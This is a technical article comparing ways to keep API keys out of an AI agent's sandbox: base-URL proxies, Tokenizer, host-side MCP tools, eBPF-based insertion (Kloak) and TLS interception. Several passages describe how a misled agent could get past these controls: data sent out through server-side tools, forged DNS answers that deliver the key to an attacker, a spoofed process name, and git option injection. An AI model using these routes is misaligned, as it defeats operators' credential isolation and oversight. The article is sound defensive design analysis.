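Many API clients build each address from a base URL and a path, and let the user change the base. Claude Code reads its base URL from an environment variable. If an operator runs a key-inserting proxy on port 8080, the setting is:

```
export ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL=http://127.0.0.1:8080
```

Claude Code then sends its model requests to http://127.0.0.1:8080/v1/messages instead of https://api.anthropic.com/v1/messages. The new address begins with http, so the request reaches the proxy as readable text. Anthropic notes that the variable redirects only model requests. Git, npm and scripts that the agent runs still connect to their own hosts.

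The unencrypted connection is safe only if nobody else can read it. One of Anthropic's setups gives the container no network. The proxy listens on a Unix socket, a channel between processes on the same machine, and the operator mounts that socket into the container. A relay inside the container passes traffic from a local port to the socket.

A proxy on another machine should use HTTPS, which doesn't require interception either. Anthropic's example address is https://llm-gateway.example.com. A company that owns such a name can get an ordinary certificate for it from a public CA that the client already trusts. If the company uses a private CA instead, the client has to trust that CA, but name constraints can limit it to the gateway's name.

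Changing the address does not remove the real credential from the sandbox. Anthropic explains that if a user sets only ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL, a saved claude.ai login remains the active credential. The operator should keep that login out of the sandbox and set ANTHROPIC_AUTH_TOKEN to a token that works only at the gateway. An organisation can also set the address in its managed settings, and Anthropic states that a developer's shell cannot override it. This setting applies to Claude Code but not to scripts the agent writes.

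Whoever sets the base URL decides which server receives the client's credential. Codex has similar settings, and according to OpenAI's *Advanced Configuration*, it ignores them in a repository's configuration file and prints a warning. The list of ignored settings doesn't include `permissions`, where users write Codex's interception hooks. However, Codex loads a repository's configuration only if the user has marked the project as trusted.

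### One request through OpenAI's proxy

OpenAI's *codex-responses-api-proxy* is a small program for this purpose. It forwards requests to the Responses API, through which Codex calls OpenAI's models. A user with administrator rights starts it like this:

```
printenv OPENAI_API_KEY | env -u OPENAI_API_KEY \
  codex-responses-api-proxy --server-info /tmp/server-info.json
```

The first command passes the key to the proxy through a pipe, and `env -u` removes it from the proxy's environment variables. The proxy chooses a free port on 127.0.0.1 and writes the number to the file. A second user, without administrator rights, starts Codex with a base URL that contains this port. If the port is 50123, a request proceeds as follows:

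1. Codex opens an unencrypted connection to 127.0.0.1:50123 and sends `POST /v1/responses` with the prompt in the body.
2. The proxy checks the method and path. It answers any other request with a 403 error, even one that only adds a query string to the same path.
3. The proxy discards any Authorization header that Codex sent, adds one with the real key, and changes the Host header to api.openai.com. It leaves the other headers and the body as they were.
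4. The proxy opens a TLS connection to api.openai.com, as any other client would, and sends the request.
5. The proxy passes OpenAI's response back to Codex.

The only TLS handshake takes place in step 4, between the proxy and OpenAI. Codex never receives a certificate, so its trust store doesn't matter. The proxy still has to verify OpenAI's certificate, as an intercepting proxy does.

Allowing only one method and path limits what a misled agent can do with the key. The agent can't list the account's stored files, for example, because that request uses a different path. But OpenAI doesn't describe a password for callers, so any program that can reach the port can make model calls at the owner's expense. The proxy also doesn't restrict the request body, and a Responses API request can tell OpenAI's servers to search the web or contact a remote tool server. A misled agent might use this to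 send data out. Anthropic's guide warns about allowed domains that can trigger other network requests.

OpenAI's proxy also protects the key in memory. It overwrites the buffer into which it read the key and asks the operating system not to write the remaining copy to disk. Running the proxy under a different user account from the agent's matters more, because it prevents the agent's commands from inspecting the process. An optional log hides the Authorization header and cookies but records the bodies in full, so it needs the same care as an intercepting proxy's log.

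A proxy that the client addresses by name doesn't always have to read the prompt. Tinfoil runs models in secure enclaves, which are isolated areas of a server's hardware. Its client library encrypts the request for the enclave, and the customer's own proxy adds the API key and forwards the encrypted content. Both the client and the service must support Tinfoil's scheme. An intercepting proxy works with any ordinary HTTPS service, but it decrypts everything it intercepts.

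### Plain HTTP through one proxy for many services

A base URL covers one service at a time. The hosting company Fly.io wanted to handle keys for many services and considered writing a small trusted program for each. Fly.io's *Tokenized Tokens* calls this cumbersome and describes Tokenizer, the general proxy the company built instead.

Programs use Tokenizer as an ordinary HTTP proxy and write addresses that begin with http, such as http://api.github.com/user. For these addresses, an HTTP client sends the proxy the whole request in readable form instead of asking for a CONNECT tunnel. Tokenizer adds the key and contacts the service over HTTPS. Because the request reaches Tokenizer in readable form, the connection to it has to run over a private or separately encrypted network.

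Tokenizer doesn't store the secrets it inserts. The program holds each secret in encrypted form and sends it in an extra header, and only Tokenizer has the private key that decrypts it. As with other substituting proxies, the owner can restrict each secret to a list of hosts.

A tutorial from the software company ZenML uses the same kind of request. In ZenML's *Credential Proxy*, an agent fetches a page from a mock wiki with this command:

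```
curl -s http://wiki.local/snippets/durability
```

The proxy adds the wiki's token and the wiki returns the page. If the agent bypasses the proxy, the wiki returns a 401 error. ZenML notes that in this demonstration the proxy adds the token to every request for the host, whatever its path or method.

Programs with a fixed https address can't use this arrangement. *proxypilot*, by timflyio, therefore puts an intercepting proxy in front of Tokenizer so that GitHub's `gh` tool, curl and the Anthropic and OpenAI client libraries can keep calling their usual addresses. The sandbox's hosts file points api.github.com to the intercepting proxy, which makes leaf certificates with its own CA, which the sandbox trusts. The intercepting proxy has the GitHub token only in encrypted form and sends it to Tokenizer with each request. Someone who copied everything the intercepting proxy holds would get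 its signing key but not the real token.

### A tool that makes the request outside the sandbox

With MCP, the agent can call a tool instead of sending the HTTPS request itself, and a program outside the sandbox does the authenticated work. In Anthropic's example, the agent sends git commands to an MCP server, which forwards them to a git proxy on the host. The proxy adds the credentials and opens its own connection to the remote repository, so there is no encrypted request from the sandbox to edit.

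A tool can also allow less than the key behind it. For example, it can let an agent read an issue but not delete the repository, even if the key permits both. ZenML's tutorial moves on to such tools in its next stage for a different reason. It describes extracting results from curl's text output as too brittle for tasks such as filing a ticket.

This approach requires a tool for each service, and existing programs can't use these tools. For example, if the agent runs a test suite that calls GitHub's API, the tests still send their own HTTPS requests.

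Reacher, a small project that provides tools for Claude, reduces this work with one general tool. The operator maps each domain to an environment variable on the server. When Claude calls `fetch_external` with an address, Reacher looks up the domain and adds the matching token. But this tool can request any page on a domain, so it is much less restricted than a dedicated tool, and less safe.

Tools on the host must also handle their input carefully. If a git tool pasted the agent's text into a command line, for example, the agent could add options that make git run another program on the host.

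### Changing the request on the client's machine

The request is readable inside the program until the TLS library encrypts it. Linux can run small programs in its kernel, known as eBPF programs, when a process calls a chosen function. Pixie, a monitoring tool, uses them only to observe the text passed to `SSL_write`, the OpenSSL function that encrypts it. For containers running on Kubernetes, spinningfactory's *Kloak* (2026) uses the same mechanism to insert secrets.

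Kloak gives the program a placeholder of the same length as the real key. When the program passes a request to the TLS library, Kloak finds the placeholder and checks where the connection goes. The library encrypts the placeholder, and Kloak edits the encrypted bytes as they leave the machine. This is the exclusive-or edit that a proxy on the network can't complete, because it can't compute a matching authentication tag. In AES-GCM, the tag is:

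```
T = GHASH(H; A, C) ⊕ E(K, J)        H = E(K, 0)
```

Here *K* is the client's write key, *E* is AES encryption, *A* is the record's header, *C* is the ciphertext and *J* comes from the nonce. GHASH combines the *m* blocks of its input by multiplying each one by a power of *H* and adding the results, where addition is exclusive-or. Suppose the edit changes block *i* by *D_i*, which is zero except where the placeholder sits. The new tag is then:

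```
T′ = T ⊕ D_1·H^m ⊕ D_2·H^(m−1) ⊕ … ⊕ D_m·H
```

Whoever has *H* can correct the tag without decrypting the record. A remote proxy can't compute *H* because it lacks the write key, but the client machine's kernel can read the program's memory. The placeholder must be as long as the secret that replaces it so that the record's header and number of blocks stay the same.

The client still connects directly to the service and receives its genuine certificate, so certificate pins, client certificates and Python's strict certificate checks cause no problems. The sandbox also needs no extra CA.

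Kloak's documentation and its developers at spinning-factory disagree about how it makes the change. The documentation describes the edit above for Go programs, and a second method that replaces the placeholder in readable text before encryption. In a Hacker News discussion, the developers wrote that they never change the program's own memory, because a hostile program could read the key back from it. An operator who wants to run an agent's code under Kloak should find out which account is right for the version they install.

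The two accounts also differ on which programs Kloak supports. The documentation includes Node.js, which it says uses the BoringSSL library. The developers limited support to OpenSSL 3.0 to 3.5 and Go 1.25 and 1.26, and planned to add BoringSSL later. Each library needs its own hook. Sivko (2026), in *Instrumenting Rust TLS with eBPF*, describes OpenSSL as straightforward to trace and rustls, a library for Rust programs, as much harder. A program with an unsupported library would send the placeholder unchanged, and the service would refuse it.

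Kloak also requires Linux 5.17 or later and a privileged process on every machine in the cluster. It can't yet handle keys that programs use to sign requests.

Kloak's destination check may be its weakest part when the agent is untrusted. Kloak watches DNS answers, records which IP addresses belong to the allowed host, and inserts the key only on connections to those addresses. The developers admit that this filter isn't perfect. With interception, the trusted proxy can verify the server's certificate, but with Kloak only the client does, and the operator doesn't trust the client. The documentation doesn't explain how Kloak recognises a forged DNS answer. If Kloak can't, a misled agent could send itself an answer that assigns api.github.com to an attacker's address, connect there and deliver the real key.

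Kloak's demonstration also shows the danger of services that send request headers back. It calls httpbin.org, a testing site that does this, and the real secrets appear in the program's log.

A second system, from Riptides, adds OpenAI keys and AWS request signatures in the kernel. Riptides' *Zero-Touch Secrets* doesn't explain how the product handles TLS or describe any limitations. Its examples identify the permitted program by process name, such as `aws`. If that were the only check, an agent could give its own script the same name and receive the credential.

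### What each arrangement demands

| Arrangement | What the operator needs | What it doesn't cover |
|---|---|---|
| Base URL | A client with a setting for the address | Programs with a fixed address |
| Plain HTTP proxy | A client that accepts an http address, and a private path to the proxy | Programs that insist on HTTPS |
| Tool outside the sandbox | A tool for each service, or one general fetch tool | Existing programs that send their own requests |
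| Editing on the client's machine | Control of the kernel and a supported TLS library | Other libraries and, in Kloak, signed requests |
| Interception | A CA in the trust store of every program | Pinned programs |

### When interception is still necessary

A proxy on the network has to intercept TLS when the operator can't reconfigure the program, the program addresses the real HTTPS host, and the request must change in transit. Rules that depend on the encrypted content, such as the read-only mode of Codex's intercepting proxy, also require decryption. Kloak can work under all three conditions without a forged certificate, but only where the operator controls the kernel and the program uses a supported library.

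**A model SDK**, the client library for a model provider's API, normally doesn't meet the first condition. Both Anthropic's and OpenAI's libraries accept a base URL, so the operator can send their requests to a proxy like OpenAI's. Interception is needed only if the code using the library hard-codes the address or the operator wants to leave every setting at its default, as in proxypilot.

**Git over HTTPS** looks harder, because the address of the repository is often written into a project's files. But git can replace the start of an address before it connects:

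```
git config --global \
  url."http://127.0.0.1:8080/github/".insteadOf "https://github.com/"
```

With this setting, `git clone https://github.com/org/repo` sends its requests to the local proxy, which adds the credential and forwards them to GitHub. The proxy can also allow downloads and refuse uploads, since git requests the `git-upload-pack` service to fetch and `git-receive-pack` to push. The setting affects only git. The `gh` tool calls api.github.com directly, so it still needs interception or a separate tool on the host.

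**An arbitrary script** may or may not need interception. If the agent writes the script, the operator can instruct it to use the proxy's address. If the agent forgets, the service will return an authentication error, the agent can correct the script, and the key stays outside the sandbox. But the script may import a package with an https address built in, or the agent may run a program it has just downloaded. The operator can't prepare a setting or a tool for code they haven't seen, so if such code needs a key, the proxy has to intercept its connection.
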